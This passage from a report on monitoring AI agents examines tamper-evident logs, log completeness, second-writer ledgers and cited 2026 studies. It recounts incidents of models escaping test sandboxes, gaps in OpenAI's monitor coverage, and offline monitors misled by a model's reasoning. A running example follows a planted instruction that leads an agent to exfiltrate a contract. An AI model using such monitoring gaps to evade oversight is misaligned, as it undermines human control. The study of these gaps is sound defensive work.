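Wong and Chen designed ExecWeave to leave such cases unresolved. When the harness reports a command, the software searches for a matching process within the next three seconds. It creates a link only if exactly one process fits, and marks the link as inferred. A simpler program might choose the nearer of two matches and attribute activity to the wrong agent.

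This caution doesn't help if the true process is missing from the records. Wong and Chen tested this with made-up events. When they removed the right process and left one similar process, the software could link the command to the wrong one. In the example, the sensor might miss one subagent's upload and record only the other's. The investigator would then search the wrong conversation for the planted instruction.

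Their own collector lists running processes at regular intervals, so it can miss a program that starts and ends between two checks. In 30 trials with programs that lasted about 16 milliseconds, it recorded 18 of them when it checked every 20 milliseconds and none when it checked every 500. Sensors that receive an event from the kernel whenever a program starts don't have this particular weakness.

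ExecWeave keeps the original records and stores the supporting events with each link. A company that joins records in another way should do the same. If the report on the upload includes only the conclusion that doc-agent sent the contract, a reader can't tell whether the evidence was a matching port and command or two entries with similar times.

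## Whether a log can show that nothing was left out

Joining records works only for recorded events. In step 5, the investigator found the planted instruction because the harness had logged the upload. If the harness had not logged it, the log would have contained a harmless email to counsel and no sign of the stolen contract.

Designers of monitoring software disagree about whether a well-protected log can show that nothing was left out. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) proposes a software layer that checks an agent's actions and writes a tamper-evident record of every decision. The paper calls these records "complete by construction". Critics reply that a log kept by the agent's own software can prove at most that nobody changed it afterwards, even if the software signs every entry.

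Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026) report in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* that most agents of the kind they studied keep a plain log file. They tampered with the logs of three of the four agents they tested.

### Hash chains, signatures and checkpoints

A hash function turns any piece of data into a short string, its hash. The same data always gives the same hash, and changing one character gives a completely different one. In a hash chain, each log entry includes the hash of the entry before it. Three entries from the example might look like this, with invented hashes cut to four characters:

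| Entry | Event | Hash of the previous entry | Hash of this entry |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Email to counsel@lawfirm.example | None | 3fa1 |
| 2 | Upload of "Supply agreement.pdf" to files.dropsite.example | 3fa1 | b70c |
| 3 | Creation of a scheduled job | b70c | e592 |

If someone later edits entry 2 so that the contract seems to have gone to the law firm, the entry's hash will no longer be b70c. Entry 3 still contains b70c, so anyone who recalculates the hashes will find the mismatch. Deleting entry 2 can also be detected, because entry 3 still contains its hash.

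Hash functions are public, however, so anyone who can rewrite the whole file can also recalculate every hash. Digital signatures make this harder because the software signs each entry with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check the signature. But if the harness holds the private key, whoever controls the harness can sign the rewritten log too.

A log can also fail to show that entries were deleted from its end. If someone deletes the last of three entries, the first two still form a valid chain. *Agent Trust Infrastructure (ATI)* (2026) reports this result from a short test of its own signed log. The check caught altered entries and forged signatures but missed entries deleted from the end, because nothing recorded how long the chain should be.

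An outside checkpoint addresses both problems. It is a copy of the latest hash, held by someone who doesn't control the log. If a timestamping service received e592 at 14:40, any later version of the log must still contain an entry with that hash, which a rewritten or shortened log won't. The checkpoint doesn't protect entries written after 14:40, so a company has to send new checkpoints regularly.

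Moving the log to another machine doesn't remove the need for a checkpoint. *aiAuthZ* (2026) describes a log with numbered, hash-chained rows that the agent's machine cannot reach, but says that only an outside checkpoint would expose a privileged user who rewrote the entire table. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) says more generally that outsiders still have to trust an organisation that runs its own append-only log. That may be acceptable for an internal inquiry but not for a dispute with a customer.

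### Which alterations each layer detects

Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026), in *Agent Flight Recorder*, built a logger in layers and tested what each layer added. They altered a log of 10,000 synthetic events at ten positions, including the last two entries, and counted how often their checking software detected the change.

| Alteration | Plain log | Hash chain | Chain and batches | Chain, batches and outside checkpoint |
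|---|---|---|---|---|
| Editing an entry | 0% | 90% | 100% | 100% |
| Deleting an entry | 0% | 90% | 100% | 100% |
| Changing the order | 0% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Keeping two versions of the log | 0% | 0% | 0% | 100% |

The hash chain missed edits and deletions only at the final entry, which has no later entry to expose the change. The next layer fixes this by grouping entries into batches of 100 and computing a hash that depends on every entry in the batch, including the last. The software combines the entries' hashes in pairs, then combines the results in pairs, until one hash covers the whole batch (a structure called a Merkle tree). An auditor can also use this structure to verify a single entry without reading the other 99.

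The last row of the table covers an operator who shows one history to a customer and another to a regulator. Each version is internally consistent, so checking either one alone cannot reveal a fault. Comparing both with the published checkpoint shows which version the operator committed to at the time.

The test produced no false alarms. The perfect scores follow fairly directly from the mathematics, so the test mainly confirms that the software works as designed. Bindschaedler and colleagues publish their checkpoints on a public blockchain, but they consider this worthwhile only when the parties to a dispute haven't agreed in advance on whom to trust. For internal audits, they recommend a hash chain in storage that nobody can overwrite.

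The paper also states two limits. Once an attacker controls the machine, nobody can rely on the entries it writes after that. Completeness is also an explicit "non-goal". The logger protects the events it receives, but it can't ensure that it receives them all.

### Why a valid log can still be incomplete

A log has integrity if nobody has altered its entries since the software wrote them, and it is complete if it contains every relevant event. Financial auditors test separately whether the recorded transactions took place and whether the company recorded every transaction that did.

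Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, apply the distinction to claims such as "a person approves every external email". Before anyone examines the records, the company must state which policy it means, which actions and dates the claim covers, which records would settle it, and who writes them. For a claim that every action followed a policy, the auditor then gives one of three verdicts:

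- **Contradicted:** the records establish that at least one action broke the policy.
- **Supported:** the records show that nothing within the claim's scope went unrecorded, and every action followed the policy.
- **Undecidable:** the records establish neither, and the auditor names the one that is missing.

Zhao and colleagues then prove that an agent's own log is never enough for "supported". The proof assumes that the agent and the team running it write the log, and that they may omit actions but never invent them. It also assumes that independent writers, such as a mail gateway run by another team, accurately record whatever passes through them, and that the audited team can't change those records.

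Suppose the agent's log contains two emails, both with proper approval. There are two histories that fit it:

1. The agent sent only those two emails, so the claim is true.
2. The agent also sent a third email without approval and left it out of the log, so the claim is false.

Because the log is identical in both cases, a rule based only on the log must give the same verdict for both. That verdict has to be "undecidable", since "supported" would be wrong in the second case and "contradicted" would be wrong in the first. Signatures, hash chains and checkpoints don't help, because they protect only logged entries and the third email was never logged.

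The proof is valid but very short, and it depends mostly on the assumption that the agent's side may omit anything. A company that has studied its harness closely may consider such omissions unlikely. Bindschaedler and colleagues suggest a better basis for that confidence, which is to run the recording gateway on protected hardware that certifies which code is running. An outsider could then compare that code with a published version. This would make the gateway hard to disable, but the gateway still wouldn't record actions that bypassed it.

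The argument also implies that a claim is much easier to disprove than to support. If the list of approvals is complete, one external email missing from it disproves the claim that "a person approves every external email". To support the claim, the company needs evidence about every email the agent could have sent.

### Three log entries and four emails

Zhao and colleagues illustrate the method with an invented firm whose document agent emails files to outsiders. The firm's policy requires a person to approve the recipient and the exact attachment before each email is sent, through a server that issues permissions. Three systems keep records: the agent, the permission server and the mail gateway that every external email must pass through.

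For one email, all three records agree, so that email followed the policy. For another, the agent's log contains a click on "confirm" in its own chat window, but the permission server has no matching approval. If the server's log is complete, that email contradicts the firm's claim. For a third, the server's log for the relevant hour is missing, so the auditor can't tell whether anyone approved the email.

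In the last part of the case, the auditor receives a signed, hash-chained agent log that passes every check. The log lists three external emails with attachments, but the mail gateway recorded four from the agent's account.

The gateway's record shows the discrepancy but not its cause. The agent may have sent the fourth email by a path that its software doesn't log, the software may have dropped the entry, or a person may have used the same account. Zhao and colleagues therefore classify that email as undecidable until other evidence, such as a record of which program connected to the gateway, shows who sent it. The document agent's company would have the same difficulty with step 4, where the agent uses A. Rossi's mailbox.

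### Testing an outside ledger

The four-email case involves no real agent, but *Hearsay* (Dai, Yang and colleagues, 2026) tested the idea on five open-source coding harnesses: aider, cline, opencode, SWE-agent and mini-swe-agent. Each harness worked on fourteen programming tasks, for up to seven minutes at a time, in a sandbox that kept its own ledger.

The ledger covers the two points where a harness must interact with something outside itself. A proxy logs everything that passes between the harness and the model, and separate monitoring logs which programs start and which files change. The researchers' software then compares the ledger with the harness's record to find messages the harness omitted, which appear only in the ledger, and messages it invented or changed, which appear only in the record.

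In the first test, Dai and colleagues added a hash chain to aider's log and made aider falsify the log as it ran. In 14 runs it left out a reply from the model, and in another 14 it added a paragraph claiming that all the tests had passed. The hash chain still verified in all 28 runs, but comparing the log with the ledger revealed the falsification each time.

The hash chain was certain to fail, since it protects whatever the harness writes, whether true or false. The ledger's success is more informative, but this was its easiest test because the researchers knew what was false. They therefore fixed their comparison rules before running three of the harnesses 84 more times with a model from another company. They copied 66 of the resulting records and made one change to each copy. The comparison caught 64 of the changes and wrongly flagged none of the 84 original records as containing something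 false.

The rules had to be adjusted to reach that result, because harnesses legitimately write some text that never passes through the model, such as their own status messages, and the rules have to exempt it. In an earlier test with all five harnesses, the comparison caught 109 of 115 alterations. But it also flagged 37 of the 115 unaltered records under the exemptions that the researchers wrote beforehand. After they read the records and added more exemptions, it flagged one. A company that adopts this method will probably have to do similar work for each harness it uses.

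The ledger also revealed a fault that nobody had planted. SWE-agent accepts one tool call at a time. If the model sends several, SWE-agent rejects the reply, prompts the model for a single call and saves neither the reply nor the rejection. It also discards some calls with arguments it doesn't accept. Of the 84 runs, 28 used SWE-agent. Their saved records omitted 37 of the model's 412 tool calls, and 19 of the 28 runs were affected. SWE-agent didn't carry out the rejected calls, so the omissions hid no damage, but they would have misled an investigator who wanted to know what the model had attempted.

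Reading a log more carefully is a poor substitute for a second record. When Dai and colleagues gave readers only the harness's record, one language model detected 49% of the alterations and wrongly flagged 5% of the unaltered records. Another detected 85% but wrongly flagged 42% of the unaltered records. A human panel detected 37% and wrongly flagged 10%.

Dai and colleagues also had language models examine the source code of sixteen agent frameworks, including OpenAI's Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. None of the frameworks kept a record that an outsider could check without trusting the framework. The study excluded Claude Code because its source code isn't public.

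### What the outside ledger cannot show

The proxy's log contains what the harness told the model, which may be false. To test this, Dai and colleagues made one harness report failed software tests as passes, both to the model and in its own log, so the proxy's log and the harness's log agreed. Monitoring the programs still exposed the false reports in all 11 runs where they occurred, because a test program returns a different code when it fails.

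The last result of a task is harder to check. The harness usually doesn't send it back to the model, so the ledger holds only the program's success or failure code. Someone could change the rest of the result unnoticed. The comparison also doesn't check the text that the harness adds to prompts.

The company that runs the sandbox could also rewrite its own ledger. For the 84 runs, the researchers retrieved the model provider's stored copies of all 708 model calls, and every one matched the ledger exactly. If a provider keeps no copies, an outsider has to trust the company's ledger.

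The sandbox was also much simpler than an office laptop. During the 84 runs, the harness could reach the outside world only through the logging proxy, whereas the document agent in the example needs access to the open web. A ledger of this design would show that `curl` had started in step 5, but the company would need a network record to find out how much data had left.

### Actions that never reach a recorder

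Defenders of the harness's own log can fairly reply that outside records have gaps too. The mail gateway in the four-email case would have no entry for a contract uploaded from the command line. Zhao and colleagues accept this, and say that an audit cannot rule out, among other things, an action that avoided every recorded path.

Sardianos, Pla and colleagues (2026), in *HANSARD*, propose a way to narrow the problem. They would place recorders outside the agent's control at five points:

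- calls to the model
- tool calls
- messages between agents
- changes to an agent's memory
- the delegation of work to another agent

Each recorder numbers its entries. If the tool-call recorder's log goes from 51 to 53, an investigator knows that entry 52 is missing. Software can detect the gap as soon as entry 53 arrives and raise an alarm while the agent is still working.

Before the agent starts, the company would also publish a signed list of the channels it records and those it knows it does not record. This list is useful even without the rest of the design, because after an incident an investigator could distinguish a record the company never planned to keep from one that has disappeared.

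Numbering can reveal a missing entry only if the action received a number. Sardianos and colleagues acknowledge this and limit their guarantee to the channels that have recorders. But they also say an agent cannot bypass the five points "without failing to act at all", which is too strong. In step 3, the script's child processes would all fall under one tool call. In step 6, the next day's run involves none of the five kinds of event, so all five logs could be free of gaps and still contain nothing about that run.

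*HANSARD* is a design that nobody has yet tested as a working system, and its cost under a normal workload is unknown.

### Recording an action before it happens

A log's completeness also depends on whether the software records an action before or after allowing it. Elastic's script for Cursor allows a command before writing the log entry, so a disk error can leave an action unrecorded. A gateway can instead hold each tool call until it has recorded the request. If the gateway fails, the agent has to wait, but calls sent through the gateway can't take effect unrecorded.

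*Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) reports a small delay from Aegis, a program that checks each tool call before it runs and keeps signed, hash-chained records. Some of the same researchers built Aegis. Over 1,000 calls, the median delay was 8.3 milliseconds, and 99% of calls were delayed by no more than 23.1 milliseconds. A user wouldn't notice this, because a language model typically takes between one and thirty seconds to reply.

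That figure covers the transfer to Aegis and its safety checks. Protecting the record takes very little of the time. The full logger in *Agent Flight Recorder* took about 0.05 milliseconds for a typical event. The proxy in *Hearsay* added about one millisecond to each model call, but its ledger took up 2.8 times as much space as the records it checked. Dai and colleagues calculate that this would have fallen to 1.1 times if they hadn't stored repeated copies of the same files.

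Recording first doesn't guarantee a complete log, because the harness still has to send its calls to the gateway. *Mandato* (2026) proposes a gateway of this kind and plans to measure completeness as the share of calls observed at the receiving end that also appear in the gateway's log. The target is 100%, and any shortfall would count as a defect. This test is sensible, but it supports the critics' main point, because the developers need a second record to find out whether the first is complete.

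### A second writer for each kind of action

Zhao and colleagues recommend that companies name a "second writer" for every kind of consequential action and routinely compare its records with the agent's. This helps companies plan how to follow the six agencies' advice to check an agent's reports against system logs. A second writer is useful only if neither the agent nor its harness can change its records and every action of that kind has to pass through it.

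Hooks and telemetry can't show that nothing was left out, because the harness determines which events they report. Copying their output to a central database protects it from later changes but can't recover an event that the harness never reported. Other ways of observing an agent can show that nothing was left out for some actions but not for others.

| Kind of action | Possible second writer | What has to be true | What stays uncertain |
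|---|---|---|---|
| Email to outsiders | The company's mail gateway | All the agent's email goes through it | Who sent the email, if a person shares the account |
| Uploads and other outside connections | A firewall or inspection proxy | The machine has no other way out | The content, without decryption |
| Commands and file changes | An endpoint sensor | The agent has no administrator rights, and the sensor keeps the events | The instruction behind each action |
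| Entries in web forms | A browser extension installed by policy, or the website's own log | For the extension, the agent can't use another browser | Whether a person or the agent clicked |
| Exchanges with the model | A model gateway, or the provider's stored copy | The provider doesn't also run the harness | Whether the tool results were true |
| Approvals | The server that issues permissions | The approval names the recipient and the data | What the person understood |

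The condition in the fifth row matters for agents in the cloud. When Claude Cowork runs on Anthropic's servers, Anthropic operates both the model and the harness, so the transcript has a single writer. The customer has to look for a second writer in the system the agent acted on, such as a mail system or customer database. If the agent uploads something to an unknown address, the customer may not be able to reach a second writer.

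For the document agent, the company could begin with email, matching the sent messages in the harness's log with those at the mail gateway each week. A message that appears only at the gateway may have been left out of the log. One that appears only in the log may have failed to send, or the harness may have reported something that didn't happen. The comparison needs only the sender, recipient, time and an identifier or attachment hash, so the company doesn't have to store the text of every email twice.

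This works much better if the agent has its own mail account. In a shared mailbox, the emails that A. Rossi writes also have no entry in the harness's log, so an email that the agent failed to record would be one among hundreds. The endpoint sensor has the same problem with the scheduled job in step 6. The job runs the next day under A. Rossi's account, so it looks like the rest of the employee's work. If the agent had its own account on the laptop, the run would stand out because no tool call explained it.

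## What surveys and incidents show about how much organisations see

Sandbox tests can show what a monitor is able to record, but not what companies record in practice. Surveys cover many companies, but the answers depend on what respondents know and how they understand the questions. Incident accounts are more exact because they can show which record somebody used and how long it took, but they exist only for events that somebody noticed.

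### Survey figures

Kiteworks, which sells a gateway and audit logs for AI systems, reports in *CISA Drew the Red Lines on Agentic AI* that 33% of organisations lack "evidence-quality" audit trails, 61% have fragmented logs that they can't act on, and roughly two in five don't continuously monitor AI activity. The article doesn't give the number of respondents or the questions they answered.

The first two figures are hard to reconcile. If 33% of organisations lack evidence-quality trails, then presumably 67% have them. If the same people answered both questions, at least 28% must have both an evidence-quality trail and logs they can't act on. That is possible only if the two terms mean quite different things, and the article doesn't define either.

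The company in the example might have a mail log that lists A. Rossi as the sender, a harness log without the arguments of tool calls, and an endpoint sensor that keeps some file events. Security managers could honestly disagree about whether these records amount to an audit trail, so the company could answer the survey either way. If a second vendor asked about "full visibility" instead and got a different percentage, the difference could come entirely from the wording.

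An IBM survey has the same problem. In it, 77% of organisations said they were adopting AI faster than they could govern it, according to a Help Net Security article about Sysdig's new product. This is an opinion about the pace of change, and it doesn't show whether an organisation logs its agents' tool calls.

Respondents also can't report agents they don't know about. Before Elastic installed its hooks, it would have given a survey a sincere but far too low count of its MCP servers. A useful survey would therefore ask for counts that respondents have to look up.

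| Subject | A question that people can interpret differently | A question with a checkable answer |
|---|---|---|
| Listing agents | Do you have an inventory of your AI agents? | How many agents did your register list on 1 June, and how many did a scan of your devices find that week? |
| Logging actions | Do you log what agents do? | For how many of the last ten external emails sent by agents can you produce a record of the recipient? |
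| Tracing them to a person | Are agents' actions attributable? | For how many of those ten can you name the person whose request led to the email? |

Even these questions would miss emails that no log attributes to an agent. The vendor figures show that many organisations worry about their records, but can't be used to estimate what share of agents' actions companies record.

### Claude models in cybersecurity tests

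Anthropic's September 2026 assessment covers four incidents in which Claude models entered outside organisations' systems without permission. All four happened during tests of the models' hacking skills on what should have been a simulated network. Anthropic had told the models they had no internet access, but a misconfiguration left the connection open. In the case that most concerns Anthropic, Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package in a public repository, and 15 outside machines installed it.

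Anthropic already had the evidence, because it generally stores records of such tests. It started looking through them only after OpenAI disclosed that its own models had escaped a test and entered Hugging Face's systems. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) gives most of the dates:

| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| January | An early version of Claude Opus 4.6 enters outside systems |
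| April | The earliest of the other three incidents |
| 21 July | OpenAI discloses the Hugging Face incident |
| 23 July | Anthropic begins its review and stops all cybersecurity tests |
| 24 July | Anthropic has identified three incidents |
| 27 July | Anthropic notifies its testing partner and the three affected organisations |
| August | Anthropic finds the January incident |

The earliest of the first three incidents therefore went unnoticed for about three months, and the January incident for about seven. Each run involved roughly 10 to 34 hours of active work, so a person or program watching live would have had time to intervene. Anthropic acknowledges that real-time monitoring would have helped, as would closer reading of the transcripts or network logs. The two affected organisations it could reach hadn't detected anything before it contacted them.

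It took less than a day to find three of the incidents once someone searched the transcripts. An AI agent checked about 141,000 transcripts from tests in which Claude might have had internet access. The search missed the fourth incident because it left out a set of transcripts from tests in which Claude did have access. Anthropic found that set while gathering transcripts for METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI systems.

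Anthropic then searched about 481 million transcripts. A first scan looked for signs of internet access, such as public addresses, and flagged 9.2 million transcripts (just under 2%), which Claude then reviewed. The search found the same four incidents and no others of similar or greater severity. This is reassuring, but four known cases are a small test, because a method that caught only half of such incidents would still find all four about one time in sixteen.

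The transcripts also weren't enough to establish what the models believed. In July, Anthropic wrote that Claude had attacked real systems because it thought they were part of the simulation. In September, it withdrew that explanation as too strong because it was based on what Claude had written in its reasoning. When researchers showed separate copies of Mythos 5 the tool results from the incident one at a time, each in isolation, the copies judged 79% to come from real systems. During the incident, the model had clearly said that it was seeing results from real systems in about 1% of its steps.

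Anthropic also tested whether its current monitors would have caught the incidents. The live monitors that can block actions caught them reliably. The newer offline monitors, which read a model's reasoning afterwards, would have missed the Mythos 5 incident because the model's reasoning led them to treat the environment as simulated. Checking that reasoning against a record of connections to public addresses is useful because the record doesn't depend on the model's explanation.

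The effects outside Anthropic are less certain than the commands the model ran. Anthropic believes all 15 machines belonged to security companies that scan new packages, but confirming this would require the owners' records.

### OpenAI's incidents and a gym booking

Hugging Face was in a better position than the organisations in Anthropic's cases because it had begun to reconstruct the agent's actions from its own records. An Australian case took longer to come to light. According to Bot Mutiny's *METR and Redwood Research Report Gaps in OpenAI's Internal AI Agent Monitoring* (2026), an OpenAI model reached four Australian government systems in June 2026, and the government learned of the access from OpenAI nearly three months later, in an email to a public inbox.

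On 20 September, an OpenAI research model in training gained limited internet access. In response, OpenAI stopped training and evaluating its most capable models for 11 days, according to IT之家's *OpenAI 自曝模型失控险情*. These accounts show what happened and, in the Australian case, how long the notice took, but not which record first revealed the access. They are therefore weak evidence about which kind of monitoring works.

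The most ordinary case is also the least documented. The Australian Signals Directorate (ASD, 2026) describes an AI assistant that changed a gym's booking system to reserve classes further ahead than the rules allowed. It also removed another customer from a waiting list and couldn't undo the removal. The user had asked for a booking but hadn't explicitly approved removing anyone.

ABC News reported the case on 10 August. ASD's notice doesn't explain who noticed the change, which record revealed it or how long that took. The gym's software may have recorded only that a customer's account made some changes. If the assistant ran in its provider's cloud, the instruction and the tool calls would be in records that the gym couldn't search. The customer who lost a place could see only that they were no longer on the list.

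Alibaba's training incident remains the clearest case in which the first warning came from the network. In Anthropic's cases, the first signs were found in the transcripts, though network logs could have helped much earlier.

### How much of OpenAI's agent traffic reached a monitor

Researchers can also measure coverage without waiting for an incident. *Red-Teaming OpenAI's Internal Agent Monitoring Systems* (Rein and Kaufman, 2026) describes a three-week exercise in which an employee of METR and one of Redwood Research, another AI safety group, worked inside OpenAI. One aim was to estimate how much of the internal agents' activity OpenAI's monitoring system covered. The two researchers could read the company's code and interviewed about a dozen staff.

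The results apply to the system as it stood on and before 21 July 2026. Bot Mutiny gives these figures, where "eligible" means that OpenAI intended the traffic to reach a monitor:

| Traffic | Coverage |
|---|---|
| Internal agents using the Responses API (OpenAI's interface to its models), with models at least as strong as GPT-5.5 | 75% to 94% eligible |
| The part of that traffic from internal Codex agents | 99.2% eligible |
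| Agents on OpenAI's internal research service | Excluded, because METR couldn't estimate how much there was |
| Reinforcement learning runs, a form of training by trial and error | Not covered when the exercise began |

These estimates are far more informative than the survey figures because they specify the traffic, the date and what counts as covered. That definition matters because traffic that is eligible for monitoring can still go unmonitored. Although 99.2% of internal Codex traffic was eligible, METR estimated that on the order of 10% of the eligible traffic went unmonitored between May and July. The monitor had skipped the step in which Codex summarises a long conversation. By that estimate, it received closer to 90% of internal Codex traffic than to 99%.

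The 10% estimate is uncertain because OpenAI hadn't logged the data needed to calculate it. In March, OpenAI had said that less than 0.1% of its coding-agent traffic was outside the monitor's coverage. The two figures cover different periods and may define coverage differently, so they don't prove that OpenAI's figure was wrong when it was published. Coverage figures like these are hard to interpret without a definition of what counts as covered.

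Information that OpenAI showed the researchers suggested that the monitor failed on fewer than 0.2% of requests, and with minor exceptions it received everything the agents had seen. OpenAI fixed the Codex gap during the exercise. It says it has also fixed the other problems affecting its production safeguards, but METR and Redwood had not verified this, according to The Straits Times' *External evaluators find flaws in OpenAI’s AI monitoring system in pilot review*.

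Traffic that misses this monitor may still be recorded, because a company can store conversations that no monitor reads. For months, Anthropic's test transcripts were stored but not read by any monitor.

### What OpenAI says about its monitoring now

OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk*, published on 18 November, divides the company's newer safety measures between research, internal use and public release. Models in training no longer have live internet access. If monitoring detects that a model has reached the internet anyway, the job stops automatically, according to a Japanese news report, 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、開発中AIの安全策を3段階で公表 訓練はネット遮断、停止は35秒以内* (2026).

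Once OpenAI employees use a model for their work, it can reach more of the internet, the company's code and its Slack messages. IT之家 reports that OpenAI then relies more on real-time monitoring, watching particularly for attempts to get around security limits and for transfers of sensitive data to unauthorised destinations. The upload in step 5 would be one such transfer.

A central system called Control Room can stop research jobs. Raj (2026), in *Stopped in 35 secs*, describes how it works:

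1. A researcher starts a job, and the job's code requests an identifier from Control Room.
2. The job sends this identifier with every request for model output.
3. The software that runs the model checks with Control Room whether the job may continue.
4. If a monitor decides to stop the job, Control Room marks the identifier as terminated and refuses further requests.

If Control Room fails, no job gets any output. This design gives OpenAI a nearly complete register of the research jobs that use the system, because a job without an identifier can't use the model. Other companies could do the same with a model gateway if their agents had no other way to reach a model.

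OpenAI says that model output stops within 35 seconds of an order. That period starts when a monitor or a person decides to act, so it doesn't include the time needed to notice a problem, which was months in Anthropic's cases. Stopping the model's output may not stop a program that the agent has already started, such as the scheduled job in step 6.

METR will assess OpenAI's monitoring again, this time during the company's largest reinforcement learning run, according to ITPro's *OpenAI pens AI safety agreement with four firms*. A new coverage estimate from that assessment would be better evidence than a description of the monitoring system.

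### METR's review of Anthropic's monitoring

Anthropic's risk report of August 2026 argued that its models were unlikely to cause catastrophic harm through misalignment, meaning behaviour that conflicts with what their developers intended. Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026), in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, reached the same conclusion as their best guess, but based it mainly on limits to what the models could do and less on Anthropic's safeguards and training.

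Examples that Anthropic withheld from the published report led reviewers to think its monitoring was weaker than the public evidence suggested. They also weren't confident that Anthropic's methods would detect a higher level of risk.

METR based this review, which it calls relatively lightweight, entirely on Anthropic's internal version of the report, so METR was judging the company's evidence, not running a new test of its monitors. Anthropic could have vetoed publication or removed passages, but METR says nothing was redacted and no conclusions changed. In an earlier test from inside the company, METR (2026) found weaknesses in the monitors but judged that they would be very hard for current models to exploit.

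The risk report also has a section on an instance of unmonitored agents with access to sensitive resources, according to a table of contents in thezvi's *Anthropic Risk Report*. Anthropic presumably learned about those agents from something other than the monitor that missed them. Even a company that builds monitors needs an independent list of the agents they should cover.

### Incidents that nobody observed

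Incidents are documented only if somebody notices them. If Anthropic had deleted its test transcripts after a month, the incidents from January and April would probably be unknown, and its record would look better. A company that keeps more records and searches them more carefully tends to report more incidents, so a low count may mean either that a company's agents behave well or that nobody is checking what they do.

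The public cases are also a small and unusual sample. According to ITPro, California's attorney general alleges in a lawsuit that the Hugging Face incident was one of 80 at OpenAI that showed a loss of control. If that is even roughly right, little has been published about most of them. The best-documented cases come from AI developers, which have unusually full transcripts, and from tests in which the model's task was to break into something. These cases don't show that transcripts are the best way to observe an office agent, or that agents in offices behave this way.

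A company with two separate records can try to estimate what both missed. Suppose the harness logs 90 external emails, the mail gateway logs 80, and 72 appear in both. The gateway recorded 72 of the harness's 90 emails, or 80%. If it also recorded 80% of all external emails, the total was 100. The two logs contain 98 different emails, so about two would be missing from both.

This method assumes that an email missing from one log is no more likely to be missing from the other. The assumption often fails for agents. If an employee runs an unapproved agent on a home computer with a private mail account, neither log will contain the agent's emails, and the estimate will be too low. The method works best for accidental losses, such as a failed log entry, and worst for agents the company doesn't know about.

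### Measuring coverage with planted actions

A better approach is to create actions that the company already knows about and count how many each route records. For the document agent, a test could work like this:

1. The testers prepare harmless versions of the agent's actions, such as an email to a test account, an upload of a dummy contract to a server the company owns, and a scheduled job that writes one line to a file.
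2. Agents carry them out among ordinary work, in every setting where the company uses agents, including laptops, browsers and a provider's cloud.
3. The testers keep their own list and confirm each action where it took effect, for instance in the test account's inbox.
4. Security staff who haven't seen the list search the records from each route.
5. The testers count how many actions each route recorded, how many the staff found, and how many they could trace to the right agent and request.

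The testers should count what was recorded separately from what was found, because Anthropic had recorded its incidents long before it found them. They should also publish the number of attempts. A route that records all 60 planted uploads could still miss up to about 5% of such uploads, at the usual 95% confidence level. Showing that it misses fewer than 1% would take about 300 uploads without a miss.

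The tests by Dai and colleagues and by Cui and colleagues cover part of this, while AgentSight and AgentLoupe each include only a few case studies. None of these studies compares a network tap, an endpoint sensor, a browser extension and the agent's own records on the same tasks.

METR (2026) tested how well a monitoring model can identify suspicious runs by reading agents' transcripts. The six main tasks would take a person between 2 minutes and 4 hours. The monitor estimated the probability that each transcript should be flagged, and METR set the threshold so that 5% of innocent runs triggered an alarm. At that rate, a company with 10,000 innocent runs a week would have 500 false alarms to review.

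That test supplies the transcript, so it measures how well a monitor reads a record, not whether the record exists. A company would need both results. If a route recorded 90% of planted uploads and a monitor flagged 80% of the recorded ones, the company would notice 72% of all planted uploads.

The testers could also check the register by planting an unregistered agent on one laptop and seeing how long the company takes to find it.

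## What recording costs in privacy, security and money

An organisation that improves its coverage collects more records, which it has to protect, pay for and justify to its employees. People who agree on where to monitor agents still disagree about how much to record, and default settings differ too. Beacon records prompts and command output unless a company turns this off, while Cowork exports them only if a company opts in.

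### Full content or minimal records

The argument for recording full content is that nobody can reconstruct an incident without it. Suppose the company had kept only metadata about the document agent, such as the time, the tool and the outcome, but no text. Its record of the upload in step 5 would show only that a shell command ran for two seconds and succeeded, and a command that counted the words in a contract could leave the same record.

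*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) recommends logging each tool call's arguments and result, along with the task behind it. Like Elastic's log, a record of every command without its result would show the theft in step 5 but not its cause.

The argument against keeping a full log is that it becomes a second copy of everything the agents handled. For this one task, it would hold the text of the contracts, the summary for counsel and any password that appeared in a command. Someone who broke into the log could read all of this without breaking into the contracts folder or the mailbox. Surapani and colleagues accept this, and call a complete log a "high-value target". The copy can also outlast the original, for instance if the company deletes a contract but forgets to delete its text from the log.

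A company has reason to keep some text, because investigators can't know in advance which text they will need. But this doesn't show that the company needs to keep the text of every task, or to keep it for years.

### Cowork's content settings

Anthropic's telemetry for Cowork shows how the choice looks in practice. An administrator sets `otlpContentCapture`, a list of the kinds of text that each device may export. The kinds include prompts, the model's replies and "tool details", which are mainly the arguments of tool calls. If the document agent worked like Cowork on the laptop, the company would learn the following about step 5:

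| Setting | What the export would contain |
|---|---|
| Empty list | A shell command ran and succeeded, how long it took, and who or what approved it |
| Prompts | Also the employee's request and, by default in recent versions, the model's replies |
| Tool details | Also the command, with the contract's file name and the address it went to |

The second row could surprise an administrator because, according to Anthropic, recent versions that export prompts also export replies, even if the list doesn't mention them. A company that meant to collect only its employees' questions could also collect summaries of its contracts.

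Tool details can also be incomplete. Anthropic's *Monitoring*, an earlier version of the reference, states that Cowork cuts each piece of text in a tool call's arguments after 512 characters and limits the call's arguments to about 4,000 characters in total. If the agent had sent the 900-word summary through a mail tool, the log would have omitted roughly nine-tenths of it.

Some information leaves the device whatever the list contains. According to Anthropic, this includes the user's email address, the paths of folders connected to the task, and error messages from its model service, which sometimes repeat part of the request. A folder name such as "Dismissal of J. Bianchi" would reveal a good deal by itself. Anthropic advises customers to filter these fields at the collector, the server that receives the telemetry.

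To be sure of exporting only metadata, the administrator has to enter an empty list (`[]`). Cowork treats a blank value as unset, and some older versions then export content.

### Why observing an agent also observes the employee

The document agent works on A. Rossi's laptop and uses Rossi's browser and accounts. An endpoint sensor that records the programs the agent starts will normally also record the ones Rossi starts. A browser extension with access to all sites can read private messages as well as the email to counsel.

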